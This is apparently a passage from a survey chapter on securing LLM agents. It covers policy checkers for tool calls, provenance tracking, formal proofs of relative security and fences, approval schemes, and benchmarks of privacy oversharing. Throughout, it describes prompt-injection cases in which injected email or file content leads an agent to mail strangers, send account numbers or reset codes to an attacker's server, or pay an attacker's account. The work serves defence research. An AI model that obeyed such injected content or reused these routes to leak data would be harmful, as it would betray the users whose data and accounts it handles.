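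Language models can help with the labelling. *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* (2026) compared labels from OpenAI's o1 with those of human annotators, across five attributes of the tools in a benchmark. Agreement was high, with a Cohen's kappa of 0.9456 (1 is perfect agreement and 0 is the agreement expected by chance). But the model rated a web navigation tool as low sensitivity, while the humans rated it as moderate because it could facilitate phishing. Such errors matter even when overall agreement is high, because an attacker needs only one tool with too lenient a label.

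APPA marks unlabelled output as unknown rather than guessing its label at the start. The agent can work with this data until a call depends on the missing label. APPA then runs a registered procedure, called a cast, to determine the label, and blocks the call if no cast applies or the cast fails. The operator limits how permissive the resulting label can be, but if that limit allows public labels, a cast that wrongly marks a salary file as public would still let the agent publish it.

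## Checking every tool call against a written policy

The orchestrator can check each tool call against a written policy before running it. These checks can enforce the many rules that do not concern the flow of data. For example, an airline may forbid changes to basic economy bookings, and labels on the booking record will not enforce that rule.

Tools may not check whether a call follows the policy. *Reason Less, Verify More* (2026) describes customer service tools that carry out any well-formed call, so an agent that cancels a non-refundable booking receives no error. In *NOMOS*, Yu, Kim and Choi (2026) measured how often an agent broke policy on τ²-bench, a benchmark of simulated customer service conversations. The agent had the airline's policy in its prompt and faced no attacker, yet 66.3% of its calls that changed a record broke the policy.

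### One policy and two calls

The check receives the tool's name and arguments. In some designs it also receives the history of the run and the provenance (source) of each argument's value. The check then allows the call, refuses it or refers it to a person. The usual aim is least privilege, giving the agent only the permissions its task needs.

Shi, He and colleagues (2025), in *Progent*, define a small language for such policies. In a similar notation, a policy for the Project X task could be:

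```
allow read_emails when { project == "Project X" }
allow send_email  when { to == "manager@company.com" and cc.length == 0 }
refuse everything else
```

For each call, the checker takes the rules for that tool and inserts the actual arguments. The call runs only if at least one allow rule applies and no forbid rule does. Suppose the agent requests these two calls:

- send_email(to = "manager@company.com", cc = [], body = summary) meets both conditions, so the orchestrator sends the summary.
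- send_email(to = "stranger@outside.example", cc = [], body = top email) fails the first condition. No other rule allows it, so the default applies and the orchestrator refuses.

An injected call to delete mail would also fail, because no rule covers that tool. Without the condition on cc, an injection could add the stranger as a second recipient. Like a fixed plan, the policy does not restrict the body of the email.

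After a refusal, the agent still has to finish the user's task. By default, Progent returns an error in place of the tool's result. The error contains the reason, the user's request and an instruction to try other tools or arguments. A rule can instead specify that Progent stops the agent or asks the user. NOMOS returns the rule and the sentence of the written policy it is based on.

Operators can install Progent as a proxy between an existing agent and its external tools without changing the agent's code. The proxy cannot check calls to the agent's built-in tools because it never receives them. Progent can check those calls too if developers add it to the agent's code.

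### Who writes the rules

A personal assistant would need different rules for almost every request, too many for an operator to write by hand. In Progent, a model writes a policy from the user's request and revises it during the run. In Conseca (Tsai and Bagdasarian, 2025, *Contextual Agent Security*), a model writes one policy per task using only trusted information. NOMOS compiles an organisation's written policy into rules, while *Solver-Aided Verification of Policy Compliance in Tool-Augmented LLM Agents* (Winston, Winston and Just, 2026) translates such a policy into logical formulas. *PACE* (Li, Wang and colleagues, 2026) derives permissions from the user's request and tracks where each argument came from.

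| System | Policy language | Who writes the rules | What software verifies |
|---|---|---|---|
| Progent | Allow and forbid rules in JSON Schema | A model, for each task; people can add fixed rules | Whether a revised policy permits any new call |
| Conseca | Regular expressions on arguments, each with a reason | A model, for each task | Each call, but not the policy, which people can audit |
| NOMOS | Named conditions attached to tools | A model, from a document; people define the conditions | Whether each rule can work with the available tools |
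| Solver-aided checking | Formulas in SMT-LIB | People, with a model's help | Whether each call is consistent with the formulas |
| PACE | Limits on a call's effects, resources and arguments | Software, from the user's request; developers describe the tools | The provenance and authorisation of each call |

### Policies for a single task

Conseca's policy model writes a policy from the user's request, the tools' documentation and any context the developer has declared trustworthy, such as email addresses and file names. In one example, a user called Alice wants the agent to answer urgent work emails. The policy lets the agent send mail only from Alice, to addresses at work.com, with "urgent" in the subject, and forbids it to delete anything. Ordinary software applies these rules, so a prompt injection cannot change them during the run.

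The policy can still be wrong. As printed, the recipient rule checks whether the company's domain appears anywhere in the address, so it would also accept some outside addresses. The trusted context can also be wrong, because an outsider may have chosen the file name of a saved attachment.

Tsai and Bagdasarian tested a prototype on 20 file and email tasks. On average, the agent completed 14.0 tasks with no policy, 12.0 with Conseca, 12.2 under a fixed policy that forbade only deletion, and none under a fixed policy that forbade all changes. The policy against deletion did not stop the one injection they tried, an email asking the agent to forward messages about security vulnerabilities. Conseca blocked the forwarding in every task except one, in which the user had asked the agent to perform the tasks in urgent emails. The policy model had no access to those emails' requests, so it presumably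 had to write a broad policy.

Progent can update the policy as the agent gets new information. In an example from Shi and colleagues, a user asks the agent to carry out a to-do list in an email from Alice. The first policy allows only a search for that email. The list includes posting a summary of recent mail to Slack, so the policy model proposes rules for reading mail and posting to Slack. Once the agent has looked up the user's Slack name, the model proposes limiting posts to that name.

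The policy model reads tool results when it writes these proposals, so an injection can influence it. Progent therefore compares the old and new policies with an SMT solver, a program that determines whether a set of logical formulas can all be true. If A(P) is the set of calls that policy P allows, a new policy P′ takes effect automatically only if

A(P′) ⊆ A(P)

The solver looks for a call that the updated policy P′ allows and the current policy P does not. If it finds one, Progent treats the update as an expansion, which needs approval. For example, if an injection causes the model to add the stranger's address to the Project X policy, the solver finds that the update would allow an email to the stranger. Between approvals, the set of allowed calls can only shrink, a property Shi and colleagues call monotonic confinement.

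*Extending the Formalism and Theoretical Foundations of Cryptography to AI* (2026) warns that an adversarial tool result could lead Progent to relax its constraints. This criticism appears to be about a version without the solver check, but it still applies if an operator automatically approves every expansion.

Monotonic confinement also does not make a broad policy safe. In the to-do example, after someone approves the expansion, the agent may post to anyone on Slack until a later update names the recipient. Because narrowing needs no approval, an injection could cause the policy model to remove a permission the task needs.

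Operators can add fixed rules, which Progent applies before the task's policy. If a fixed rule forbids a call, the policy model cannot allow it. The task's policy decides whether to allow calls to tools that the fixed rules leave out.

With GPT-4o, Progent reduced attack success on AgentDojo from 39.9% to 1.0% with little effect on utility. On ASB, another benchmark of attacks on agents, attack success fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. In both tests, Shi and colleagues approved every policy expansion automatically to imitate a careless user. The solver check therefore never blocked an expansion, and the results measure how well the model wrote policies. The initial policy alone reduced attack success on AgentDojo to 2.5%. Three kinds of attack aimed at the policy updates raised the rate only marginally. Narisetty and colleagues also found a large reduction in attack success in a small independent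 test.

### Rules compiled from a document

A company's rules often exist in a document already. NOMOS converts the document once, before the agent starts work, into rules of the form

r = (id, type, tools, predicate, clause)

The predicate is a condition that ordinary software can evaluate, and the clause is the original sentence. A FORBIDDEN rule blocks its tools while the predicate holds, and a PRECONDITION rule blocks them until it holds. For example, "Basic economy flights cannot be modified" becomes a FORBIDDEN rule on the tool that changes flights, with the predicate cabin_is_basic_economy. If the fact a rule needs is missing, a PRECONDITION rule blocks the call but a FORBIDDEN rule allows it. The compiler therefore uses PRECONDITION rules where possible for confirmation and authorisation.

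The checker takes facts only from tool results and the user's messages. If an injection makes the agent claim that the user has approved a transfer, that claim does not satisfy a rule that requires the user's approval. An attacker who can alter the relevant field of a tool result could still supply a false fact.

NOMOS uses a language model to extract the rules from the policy document five times. Ordinary software then looks for rules that cannot work, and a majority vote decides which rules to keep. The software found defects in 29 of 79 candidate rules for an airline and 7 of 53 for a retailer. In one case, a requirement to authenticate the user first had become a rule that blocked every tool, including the two that authenticate users. Other candidates required confirmation before the agent could look up a flight. After repairs, rejections and the removal of duplicates, 10 airline rules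 and 5 retail rules remained.

A rule can pass these checks and still misstate the policy, so Yu and colleagues replay the compiled rules on recorded runs of an unprotected agent. In one test, a telecom company's policy told the agent to check that a bill was overdue before requesting payment, but the compiler produced a rule that banned payment requests for overdue bills. The replay showed that this rule would have refused 47 of 49 payment requests in successful runs.

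On τ²-bench, NOMOS reduced the share of record-changing calls that broke the policy from 66.3% to 2.6% for the airline and from 30.8% to 6.9% for the retailer. The airline agent also made fewer record-changing calls, 116 instead of 353. It completed 47.6% of tasks with the check and 39.2% without it, but the difference was not statistically significant.

To test their measurements, Yu and colleagues had Claude Sonnet 4.5 judge a sample of 160 calls. It disagreed with their rule-based checker on 77. In 30 of these, the model was wrong about facts that could be checked in the transcript, such as whether a booking made 23 hours earlier fell within a 24-hour limit. The checker was wrong in 3, and most of the other disagreements were about how to interpret the policy. An operator who used a model as the final check would have to accept factual errors like those 30.

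Winston, Winston and Just express an airline's rules as formulas and use the Z3 solver to test whether each requested call is consistent with them. The call runs if it is consistent; otherwise, the agent receives the conflicting formulas and can revise its plan up to three times.

Incomplete formulas make this test too permissive. One automatic translation of the cancellation rule amounted to

booked within 24 hours ⇒ cancellation allowed

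For a booking made 30 hours ago, the left side is false, so the formula is true whether or not the right side is. The solver can treat the cancellation as allowed without any contradiction, and the forbidden call runs. A correct formula has to list every permitted reason and exclude all others:

cancellation allowed ⇔ (booked within 24 hours ∨ another permitted reason)

Winston and colleagues found and repaired such gaps by hand. If a rule is missing, their design allows the call, whereas Progent refuses it by default.

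The check depends on a language model to extract facts, such as the time of booking, from the conversation. If the model extracts a wrong value, the solver can approve a forbidden call. On τ²-bench's airline tasks, the check reduced the share of record-changing calls that were invalid from about half to 29%. The agent also made fewer correct record-changing calls, but overall task success was slightly higher.

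### Where an argument came from

If the user does not name a recipient, a policy based on their request cannot restrict who the recipient is. Yu and colleagues found this when they ran Progent on AgentDojo's banking tasks, with the open-weight model Gemma 4 26B acting as the agent and writing the policies. The attack success rate fell from 46.5% to 5.6%. Twelve of the 16 attacks that still succeeded came from two tasks, one of which was to pay a bill stored in a file. The user had not given an account number, so the policy allowed payment to any account, including the attacker's.

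AgentDojo has no written policy, so Yu and colleagues wrote a rule for NOMOS to apply, that payments may go only to accounts the user has named or paid before. NOMOS stopped every payment to the attacker, but it also blocked payment of the genuine bill, because that account number appeared only in the file. In 8 of 288 attacked runs, the agent sent an injected payment to someone the user had paid before, which the rule allowed.

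Rules about where a value came from can reduce task completion much more in other settings. On AgentDojo's Slack tasks, making one such rule stricter reduced the number of attacks that executed from 15 in 105 runs to none. It also reduced the share of tasks the agent completed when there was no attack from 57.1% to 14.3%, because many of these tasks require it to act on names and addresses it has read.

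PACE checks where a tool call's arguments came from and whether the user authorised its effects. It first freezes the arguments so they cannot change after the check, then matches them against values from earlier in the run, for example to link an account number to the file it came from. A path check looks for routes by which secret or untrusted data could reach an unsafe effect. A permission check compares the call's effects with what the user's request authorises. Its nine requirements cover matters such as confidentiality, lasting changes, delegation and the remaining budget.

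The path check is too strict on its own because some legitimate tasks, such as forwarding an outsider's email to the user's manager, require untrusted text to reach an outgoing message. When each check was tested alone on AgentDojo, both reduced attack success from 37.4% to zero. Task completion fell from 76.8% to 13.6% with the path check and to 64.6% with the permission check.

If the permission check approves a call, the version of PACE that Li, Wang and colleagues evaluated can restore it even after the path check has blocked it. Their full security guarantee applies to a stricter version, which they did not test. Even in that version, the path check can miss text that the model has paraphrased, translated or split up, although it recognises copied values and some encodings.

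Across eight benchmarks and three models, PACE had the lowest or joint lowest attack success rate in 76 of 79 comparisons. Under the strongest type of attack on AgentDojo, PACE reduced the rate for GPT-5.6 Luna from 100% to 8.1%. In Kravchenko and colleagues' workspace runs, the same model followed no injections even without a defense, so the results evidently depend heavily on the choice of attacks and the test setup.

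Li, Wang and colleagues also ran an automated search that adapted its attacks to the defence. It succeeded on 21 of 30 targets without PACE and on none with it. With only 30 targets, the true success rate with PACE could be as high as about 11%.

### Permitted calls that do harm together

A policy can approve every call in a run and still permit a harmful sequence. Tsai and Bagdasarian note that sending one email is harmless but flooding an inbox is not. Under the Project X policy, an injection could make the agent send the manager the same summary a hundred times. A Progent rule depends only on the arguments of the current call, so it cannot count earlier calls. A sequence of permitted calls can also leak private data. For example, an agent may be allowed to read a salary file and search the web, but it could then include the salary in a search query.

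To prevent this, the checker needs a record of earlier calls. PACE's budget requirement can limit repeated actions. FORGE (Yu et al.) keeps a graph of how the events in a run depend on one another and applies rules written in Datalog, a logic language. On six selected τ²-bench tasks, it raised the share of successful runs from 58% to 98%.

*Soteria* (2026) verifies a complete plan before it runs. Each tool has a contract that states what must be true before a call and what will be true afterwards. The verifier, Dafny, uses these contracts to prove that every call meets its conditions, that the plan cannot get stuck and that no possible sequence of its calls violates the policy. The proof does not cover any effect of a tool that its contract omits.

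### Asking a person to approve

When the rules cannot settle a case, the orchestrator can ask the user. With a person reviewing the initial policy and every expansion, Progent reduced attack success on AgentDojo to 0%. However, Shi and colleagues assumed an alert reviewer who would never allow payments to arbitrary recipients and would reject any malicious address. With automatic approval, the attack success rate was 1.0%, so the rate with a real user would probably fall between 0% and 1.0% against these attacks. An attacker who disguised a request as part of the task might succeed more often.

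People who receive too many approval requests may stop reading them, a problem known as confirmation fatigue. Tsai and Bagdasarian cite research on smartphone permissions and similar systems as evidence that relying on manual confirmation can cause fatigue and lead people to grant too much access. They expect policies tailored to each task to reduce the problem, but their prototype never asked users anything. Progent needed approval for only 6% of policy updates on AgentDojo, which should help, although users may still answer those requests carelessly. Neither paper measured how real users' decisions change as requests accumulate.

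Designers also have to decide how much one approval covers. In NOMOS, each record-changing call uses up the user's confirmation, so even a retry after an error needs a new one. This keeps the agent from departing from what the user approved, but it means the user has to answer more questions. The confirmation rule caused 61% of refusals in the airline test and 84% in the retail test. When Yu and colleagues counted one confirmation as covering every change the agent had announced, the unprotected airline agent's violation rate fell from 66.3% to 36.8%.

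Approving one exact call is safer than approving a tool, which leaves the arguments open. The approval request should show the recipient and content that the orchestrator will send, because an injection could influence the model's description of them. In the Project X task, the user has already named the manager, so the system doesn't need to ask about that address. If the agent finds a new address in an email and tries to write to it, asking the user is probably worth the interruption.

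## What can be proved about a defence

A proof can cover every attack that fits a stated model of the agent and the attacker, whereas a benchmark only measures how many of its own attacks a defence stops. A proof first needs a definition of security that a useful agent can meet. Noninterference rules out many ordinary tasks because it requires that secrets never influence anything an outsider observes. Dongol instead compares the agent with a hypothetical version that ignores every injection, and calls the resulting property relative security.

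### Comparing an agent with one that never obeys

The definition applies to plan-then-execute agents with a monitor that allows or denies each tool call and each untrusted read. The reference agent runs the same plan under the same monitor, but its model never follows instructions in untrusted content. The real agent is relatively secure if all of its leaks also occur in the reference agent.

A leak involves two runs, r₁ and r₂, with different secrets, σ₁ and σ₂. The attacker supplies the same content in both runs but observes different results:

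Act(r₁) = Act(r₂) and Obs(r₁) ≠ Obs(r₂)

For every such pair, relative security requires two runs of the reference agent that have the same secrets and also leak. They must start from the same stored data and trusted inputs, but the attacker's content may differ from what the real agent received.

In one of Dongol's examples, a user called Alice asks for a summary of an email. The plan looks up her account number, reads the email and shows her a summary. An injection in the email makes the model request a web page on the attacker's server, with the account number in the address. If the number is 111 in one run and 222 in the other, the server receives two different requests. The reference agent never contacts the server, whatever the email contains, so the real agent fails the test.

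### Disclosures that the task intends

Now suppose Alice wants her agent to send her calendar to anyone who emails a meeting request. In Meeting Reply, the attacker's email instructs the agent to send the calendar instead of requesting a meeting, and the model obeys. The attacker could have obtained the same calendar with a genuine request, so the reference agent has a matching leak and Alice's agent satisfies relative security.

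In Reset Code, the agent also holds a private password reset code, and the attacker requests that too in the injection. No email would make the reference agent send the code, so this agent does not satisfy relative security.

Noninterference would reject both cases, because even the honest assistant tells outsiders when Alice is busy. A release policy that permits sharing the calendar would separate them correctly, but someone would have to write such a policy for each task. Relative security uses the plan's own behaviour as the policy. It does not test whether the agent should have obeyed, so Meeting Reply passes even though the agent sent the calendar to someone who had not asked for a meeting. That result also covers only the one injection in the example.

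The freedom to choose a different attacker input weakens the guarantee. Suppose a plan lets an outsider guess a four-digit code and replies only "right" or "wrong", while an injection makes the real agent send the whole code. For any two codes, the reference agent's replies differ if the outsider guesses one of them. The injected disclosure therefore counts as relatively secure, although a run without the injection reveals only whether one guess was right. Dongol's stricter version, uniform relative security, fixes the reference agent's input without regard to the secret, so it rejects this case.

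Relative security also preserves limits on what the plan itself reveals. If an operator can show that the reference agent discloses at most the calendar, then a relatively secure agent also discloses at most the calendar. The operator can check the reference agent's limit without considering injections.

### The fence theorem

A fence withdraws tools from an agent once it reads untrusted content. Dongol proves that a fence makes an agent relatively secure under these conditions:

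- Trusted software runs the fixed plan, and every tool call and untrusted read goes through the monitor.
- At the first untrusted read, the monitor withdraws every tool that an injection can call. No later input gives those tools back.
- Each injection causes a single tool call, not a longer program.
- The model obeys on a schedule fixed in advance. The timing cannot depend on secrets or on the monitor's answers, though an injected call may contain any data the agent holds.
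- The attacker sees the content and order of the calls that reach them, but not their timing or the calls that the monitor refuses.
- The run ends. For a loop that may run forever, the model must also be unable to keep obeying injections forever.

The result then holds for every plan and every way the model might interpret untrusted text as an instruction to call a withdrawn tool.

To prove this, Dongol compares the real agent with the reference agent step by step. Before the first untrusted read, the model has read no injection, so both agents take the same steps. The read activates the fence. After that, when the real agent requests an injected call, the monitor silently blocks it and the reference agent waits. When the real agent takes a step of the plan, the reference agent does too, and it receives the same answer because both monitors are in the same state. The attacker therefore observes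 the same calls from both agents.

The plan cannot use the withdrawn tools either, so a fence on the mail tool would also stop the agent from sending the Project X summary. Relative security does not measure this loss, because the reference agent could not send the summary either. If the operator leaves the mail tool available for the summary, the theorem no longer covers injections that send mail.

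The condition about single calls matters because an injection may do harm without calling a tool itself. In Poisoned Variable, the plan sends the attacker's email back to the attacker. An injected program replaces the stored email with a secret, and the plan then sends the secret. A fence is enough to stop such programs if the software discards their changes to the plan's data and the fence covers untrusted reads as well as calls.

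### Where the fence has to go

A plan can also raise a fence itself by calling a lock, after which the monitor refuses to send anything. Dongol compares three placements:

- Late Fence reads the attacker's email, then a secret, then locks. An injection can send the secret before the lock takes effect.
- Middle Fence reads the email, locks, and only then reads the secret. The new secret is safe, but an injection can still send private data that was already in the agent's memory, perhaps from an earlier session.
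- Early Fence locks before it reads the email. No injected message can leave, because the model has nothing to obey until sending is impossible.

Researchers first developed relative security for processors that guess which instructions come next and execute them early, which can expose secrets. On those processors, a barrier just before the existing code that leaks can be enough, and Middle Fence resembles that precaution. In an LLM agent, however, an injection adds its own leaking call, which may come at any point after the read, so the fence has to come before any point where that call could occur.

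Restoring a tool is safe only if the model starts a fresh session that retains nothing from the old content. In Stale Loop, each new trusted report restores the sending tool while the previous email is still in the model's context, and the model then follows the instructions in that email.

### Approving a tool or an exact call

Many agents have to reply after reading an email, so a permanent fence is too strict. Suppose that in each turn of a conversation, the agent reads an email, Alice approves a reply, and the agent sends it. The agent also holds private data, which it never sends under the plan.

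In Tool Approval, Alice's approval permits the next message, regardless of its content. After she approves her reply, an injection can make the model send the private data before the plan sends the reply. The injected message also uses up the approval, so the monitor blocks Alice's reply.

Call Approval permits only the exact message that Alice approved. If her reply is "Thursday" and the private data is "Tuesday", the monitor blocks the injected message and sends her reply at the planned step. If the private data is also "Thursday", the monitor allows the injected message and blocks the planned one. In both cases the attacker receives one message saying "Thursday", but in the second it arrives a step earlier.

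An attacker who sees only the content and order of messages learns nothing from this, but one who can measure the timing learns whether the private data matches Alice's reply. The agent is therefore relatively secure against only the first attacker. Holding every approved reply until a fixed time would probably stop the timing leak, but it would also slow replies.

### What the verdicts show

A budget, which limits how often an agent may use a tool, has the same weakness as Tool Approval. In Budget Race, the agent may send one message, and an injection uses it to send the reset code before the plan can send the calendar. In Budget First, the plan sends its message before it reads the email, so the limit blocks any message from the injection. The table gives nine of Dongol's 25 cases.

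| Case | Defence | Verdict | Reason |
|---|---|---|---|
| Fenced Summariser | Fence on the web tool | Secure | The tool is gone before the injection can use it |
| Budget Race | One message per run | Leaks | A budget limits how many messages go out, not which |
| Budget First | One message, sent before the read | Secure against injected messages | The plan has already spent the budget |
| Tool Approval | User approves the next message | Leaks | The approval covers any content |
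| Call Approval | User approves the exact message | Secure unless the attacker sees timing | An early reply reveals a match |
| Spotlit Summariser | Spotlighting | Leaks unless the model honours the marks | The marks do not restrict the model |
| Untagged Dual LLM | Quarantined model | Leaks | The model can quote private notes in its answer |
| Tagged Dual LLM | Quarantined model and labels | Secure unless the attacker sees refused requests | The monitor also blocks the honest reply |
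| Tagged Branch | The same labels, with a plan that branches | Leaks | The choice between two public messages reveals the secret |

Dongol considers any form of spotlighting that gives different texts different marked versions. Such a marking is reversible in principle, so for any possible model that obeys an instruction in plain text, another obeys the marked version. No such marking can therefore be guaranteed to work for every possible model, but this does not predict how often real models fail.

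In Tagged Branch, the plan sends 1 or 0 depending on the quarantined model's answer, and both values are public. An injection can make the answer depend on the user's private notes, and the message then leaks one bit about them through an implicit flow. The labels here follow CaMeL's normal mode. CaMeL's strict mode is designed to close this channel, but Dongol leaves it to future work.

Isabelle/HOL, a program that checks formal proofs, verified all the verdicts. The formal development is about 31,600 lines long, and Claude models helped to write the proofs. People still had to check that the formal definitions matched the intended ones, because Isabelle cannot detect when a correct proof is about the wrong model. The cases are small formal models of each mechanism, not tests of the named products.

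Combining or removing defences can unexpectedly change whether an agent is secure. The agent that summarises email is secure if it has only the mailbox or only the web tool, but leaks data if it has both. Removing a permission can even make a secure agent insecure, because it may remove the intended disclosure that matched an injected leak. Designers therefore have to prove that each combination is secure.

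### What the proofs leave aside

The largest exclusion is the ordinary agent loop, in which the model chooses every call. Such an agent doesn't fix a plan before it reads untrusted data, so there is no reference agent to compare it with.

Relative security also covers only leaks, so an agent that obeys an injected command to delete Alice's mail can still satisfy it. *Relativising Integrity and Robustness* (2026) extends the approach towards integrity, also with Isabelle proofs. In each of its language-model case studies, the proofs for all the fixes together took 140 to 296 lines, because they reuse a general theorem. The proof of the attack was longer, at 318 to 629 lines, because it has to go through the runs of a particular agent.

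Dongol assumes that the planner interprets the user's request correctly. If the planner mistakenly writes a plan that sends the calendar to everyone, the reference agent does the same, so the comparison detects no problem. The proofs also do not cover multi-agent systems, side channels, or tools whose reply depends on the query, such as a search engine that the attacker runs.

The fence theorem assumes that the agent does not react to the monitor, but agents commonly receive an error after a refused call and try something else. Refusals can also leak private information if outsiders see them. In Permission Probe, an injection calls an internal tool that works only if a private setting is on, so a visible refusal reveals that the setting is off.

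Dongol's fence theorem does not count a difference in the number of messages as a leak, because it compares only runs in which the same number of calls reach the attacker between reads. An injection could therefore reveal whether a secret is 0 by requesting an approved newsletter page if it is and a forbidden page otherwise. The attacker sees one more request in the first case.

### Guarantees for other kinds of agent

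*The LLMbda Calculus* covers agents that write and run code during a task, which relative security excludes. It proves a form of noninterference for every program in its language. Models choose their output at random, so the proof compares probabilities. Suppose two inputs differ only in their secrets, and let μ and ν give the probability of each result that an observer could see. The theorem guarantees a single distribution ω, with a total of at most 1, such that

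μ ≤ ω and ν ≤ ω for every possible result

If the program always finishes, μ and ν must be equal. Otherwise, secrets may affect whether it finishes, and the distance between μ and ν is at most the average probability of not finishing. If both runs fail to finish 10% of the time, the distance is at most 0.1. A failed policy check counts as not finishing.

The theorem, checked with the proof assistant Lean, applies to the software that calls the model. This precision is useful in practice, because *The LLMbda Calculus* identifies two leaks in CaMeL that informal reasoning had left open. CaMeL updates a variable's label only in the branch it runs, so a variable that keeps its old value because of a secret can remain labelled public. Its retry loop also runs outside the part that tracks labels, so each blocked attempt can reveal one bit of a secret, and repeated attempts can reveal all of it.

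The table, based on Dongol's comparison, shows how four definitions of confidentiality judge the same agents. Explicit secrecy is the guarantee that FIDES provides.

| Definition | Meeting Reply | Reset Code | Tagged Branch |
|---|---|---|---|
| Noninterference | Rejects | Rejects | Rejects |
| Release policy written for the task | Accepts | Rejects | Rejects |
| Explicit secrecy | Rejects | Rejects | Accepts |
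| Relative security | Accepts | Rejects | Rejects |

*The LLMbda Calculus* includes endorsement, which lets a program treat untrusted data as trusted, because its guarantee would otherwise be too strict for some tasks. A second theorem proves that endorsement cannot weaken the protection of secrets, but it can let an attacker influence an action. In tests on AgentDojo's banking tasks, two of 1,296 attacked runs succeeded. In both, the user asked the agent to make a payment according to a file whose contents an attacker had replaced. These attacks are consistent with the proof because the agent had explicitly endorsed the file.

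Type systems offer another kind of guarantee. Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova (2026), in *Language-Based Agent Control*, require an agent to write programs that a type checker accepts together with the developer's code. The checker rejects unsafe programs before they run. Odersky, Zhao and Xu (2026), in *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents*, use the programming language Scala 3 to track which code may use which resources. The type system can then bar code that handles classified data from any outside effect, such as a network request. Both designs rely on mature compilers, but *The LLMbda Calculus* points out that neither has a machine-checked theorem about the whole agent.

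*A Framework for Formalizing LLM Agent Security* (Siu, He and colleagues, 2026) defines security for a single run. At each step, the agent must pursue an authorised objective, take an action that serves it, follow only authenticated sources and respect limits on data. The same command to delete a file can therefore be legitimate in one run and an attack in another. This definition covers hijacking as well as leaks, but deciding whether a run is secure requires knowing which text the model was following. The framework represents that knowledge with ideal functions that may have no perfect implementation. Relative security does not require this knowledge because it compares what the attacker can observe.

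Both approaches give a yes-or-no verdict. *GIF* (2026) instead measures how strongly each part of a model's input influences its output, including tool arguments and messages to other agents.

### From a proof to a running system

A theorem applies to a product only if the product meets the theorem's assumptions. *Alignment Contracts for Agentic Security Systems* (2026) explicitly separates its theorems from those assumptions. The Lean proof assistant checks that the conclusions follow from the definitions, but not that the deployed software intercepts every action. *Agenra* (2026), which verifies a system for authorising tool calls, proves some results about the deployed checking functions and others about companion models. Its proofs do not establish that developers described the tools correctly or that a tool has no hidden effects.

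A proof's assumptions can contain most of the difficulty. *Provably Secure Agent Guardrail* (2026) proves that every state an agent reaches satisfies fixed safety rules. The proof starts from a safe state and shows that each permitted step preserves safety. It assumes that the system has faithfully translated natural language into formal statements, and the paper calls faithful translation an open research problem. Winston and colleagues' checker depends on a similar translation.

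*PerMIT* (2026) protects an agent's long-term memory. Its results hold however the protected model behaves, so they do not require it to resist injections. Some of them still depend on how competent the inspectors of stored content are, which a proof assistant cannot establish.

### Limits that no design can avoid

Other proofs show what defences cannot do. *The Defense Trilemma* (2026) considers software that rewrites each prompt before the model receives it. If similar prompts get similar rewrites and safe prompts stay unchanged, the rewriting cannot make every output safe. As a prompt changes gradually from safe to unsafe, it passes through a borderline version that the software must leave unchanged. The result does not apply to systems that can reject a prompt or to monitors on tool calls.

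*AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections* (2026) makes a broader argument and formalises part of it. An attacker can supply a false claim that, if true, would make an action appropriate, such as a notice that a supplier has changed its bank account. Unless the agent can verify the claim, any fixed policy that blocks the false notice also blocks a genuine one. The fence theorem is compatible with this argument because a fence blocks both the false notice and the genuine one.

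## Enforcing privacy when no attacker is present

The reference agent in Dongol's proofs never obeys an injection, but it can still send private information to someone who should not have it. *AgentCIScope* (Guo, Chen and colleagues, 2026) describes a recruiter who asks an agent to send a hiring manager an update on a candidate. The agent, which runs on OpenAI's GPT-6 Astra, finds the candidate's background check among the recruiter's files and includes details from it in the update. The manager should receive the update but does not need the background check.

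A fixed plan would allow this message, because the user asked for it. An integrity policy would also allow it if the files are trusted. A confidentiality label would stop it only if someone had already decided that hiring managers may not read background checks.

### Judging a disclosure by its context

Helen Nissenbaum's 2004 theory of contextual integrity defines privacy as the appropriate flow of information. *PrivacyFlow* (Staab, Wollschläger and colleagues, 2026) describes each flow by five features: the sender, the recipient, the subject, the type of information and the terms on which it is shared. A flow violates privacy if it departs from the norms of the setting the information came from.

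Suppose a user takes medication for epilepsy. Their agent answers questions from a doctor's office before an appointment, and later answers a recruiter's questions about a job interview.

| Feature | Doctor's office | Employer |
|---|---|---|
| Sender | The user's agent | The user's agent |
| Recipient | A medical practice | A recruiter |
| Subject | The user | The user |
| Type of information | Medication | Medication |
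| Terms | For treatment, in medical confidence | For arranging an interview |
| Appropriate? | Yes | No |

A label with a list of permitted readers can handle this case, since the doctor's office is on the list and the employer is not. But if the user applies for a job at the clinic that treats them, the label would also allow the application to mention the medication, because the clinic is a permitted reader. An operator could treat the clinic's doctors and its personnel department as separate readers, but the software would then need to know which of them it is writing to.

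Reader lists also cannot express some rules about combining data. Summers and Wu (2026), in *Data Flow Control*, give the example of a hospital that lets a physician see customer profiles and health records, but forbids combining them unless the customer has consented. If the physician may read both, the usual rule for joining labels allows the combination:

{physician, billing clerk} ∩ {physician, nurse} = {physician}

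The same rule is too strict for statistics. The average age of a thousand patients may be harmless to publish, but its label would restrict it to people who may read all thousand records.

### How often agents overshare

Staab and colleagues gave a personal agent called OpenClaw 39 sequences of tasks. The agent disclosed something inappropriate in 87 of the 240 steps they evaluated, and in 67 of those 87 it also completed the user's task. For example, when it scheduled a termination meeting, it revealed a covert investigation to the employee being fired.

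The PrivacyBench benchmark has 986 sequences of four to eight tasks involving email, calendars and notes. Each sensitive fact has a list of people who may know it, but the agent never receives the list and has to infer it from the situation. Because the correct answers are themselves reader lists, the harder problem often seems to be working out who belongs on them.

Six models avoided leaks in 68.1% to 89.5% of individual steps, but in only 13.0% to 52.9% of whole sequences. If the models with the lowest and highest step rates also had the lowest and highest sequence rates, the sequence rates are close to what independent mistakes over six steps would produce, since 0.681⁶ is about 10% and 0.895⁶ is about 51%.

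Guo, Chen and colleagues tested 12 combinations of model and agent software on 936 tasks. They worded the requests to encourage oversharing, for example by asking for a self-contained briefing, but never asked for protected information. The leakage rates they measured may therefore overstate everyday leakage. Running each task five times raised the share of tasks with a leak by 4 to 19 percentage points.

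*AgentCIBench*, the benchmark in *Capable but Careless* (2026), tests agents that operate a computer, while *CI-Work* (2026) simulates office work. The table gives the range of failures on each benchmark.

| Benchmark | What counts as a failure | Lowest rate | Highest rate |
|---|---|---|---|
| PrivacyBench | A sequence with at least one leak | 47.1% | 87.0% |
| AgentCIScope | A task with a leak in a single run | 32.5% | 94.4% |
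| AgentCIBench | A leak in a task the agent did not refuse | 14.0% | 98.3% |
| CI-Work | A privacy violation in an office task | 15.8% | 50.9% |

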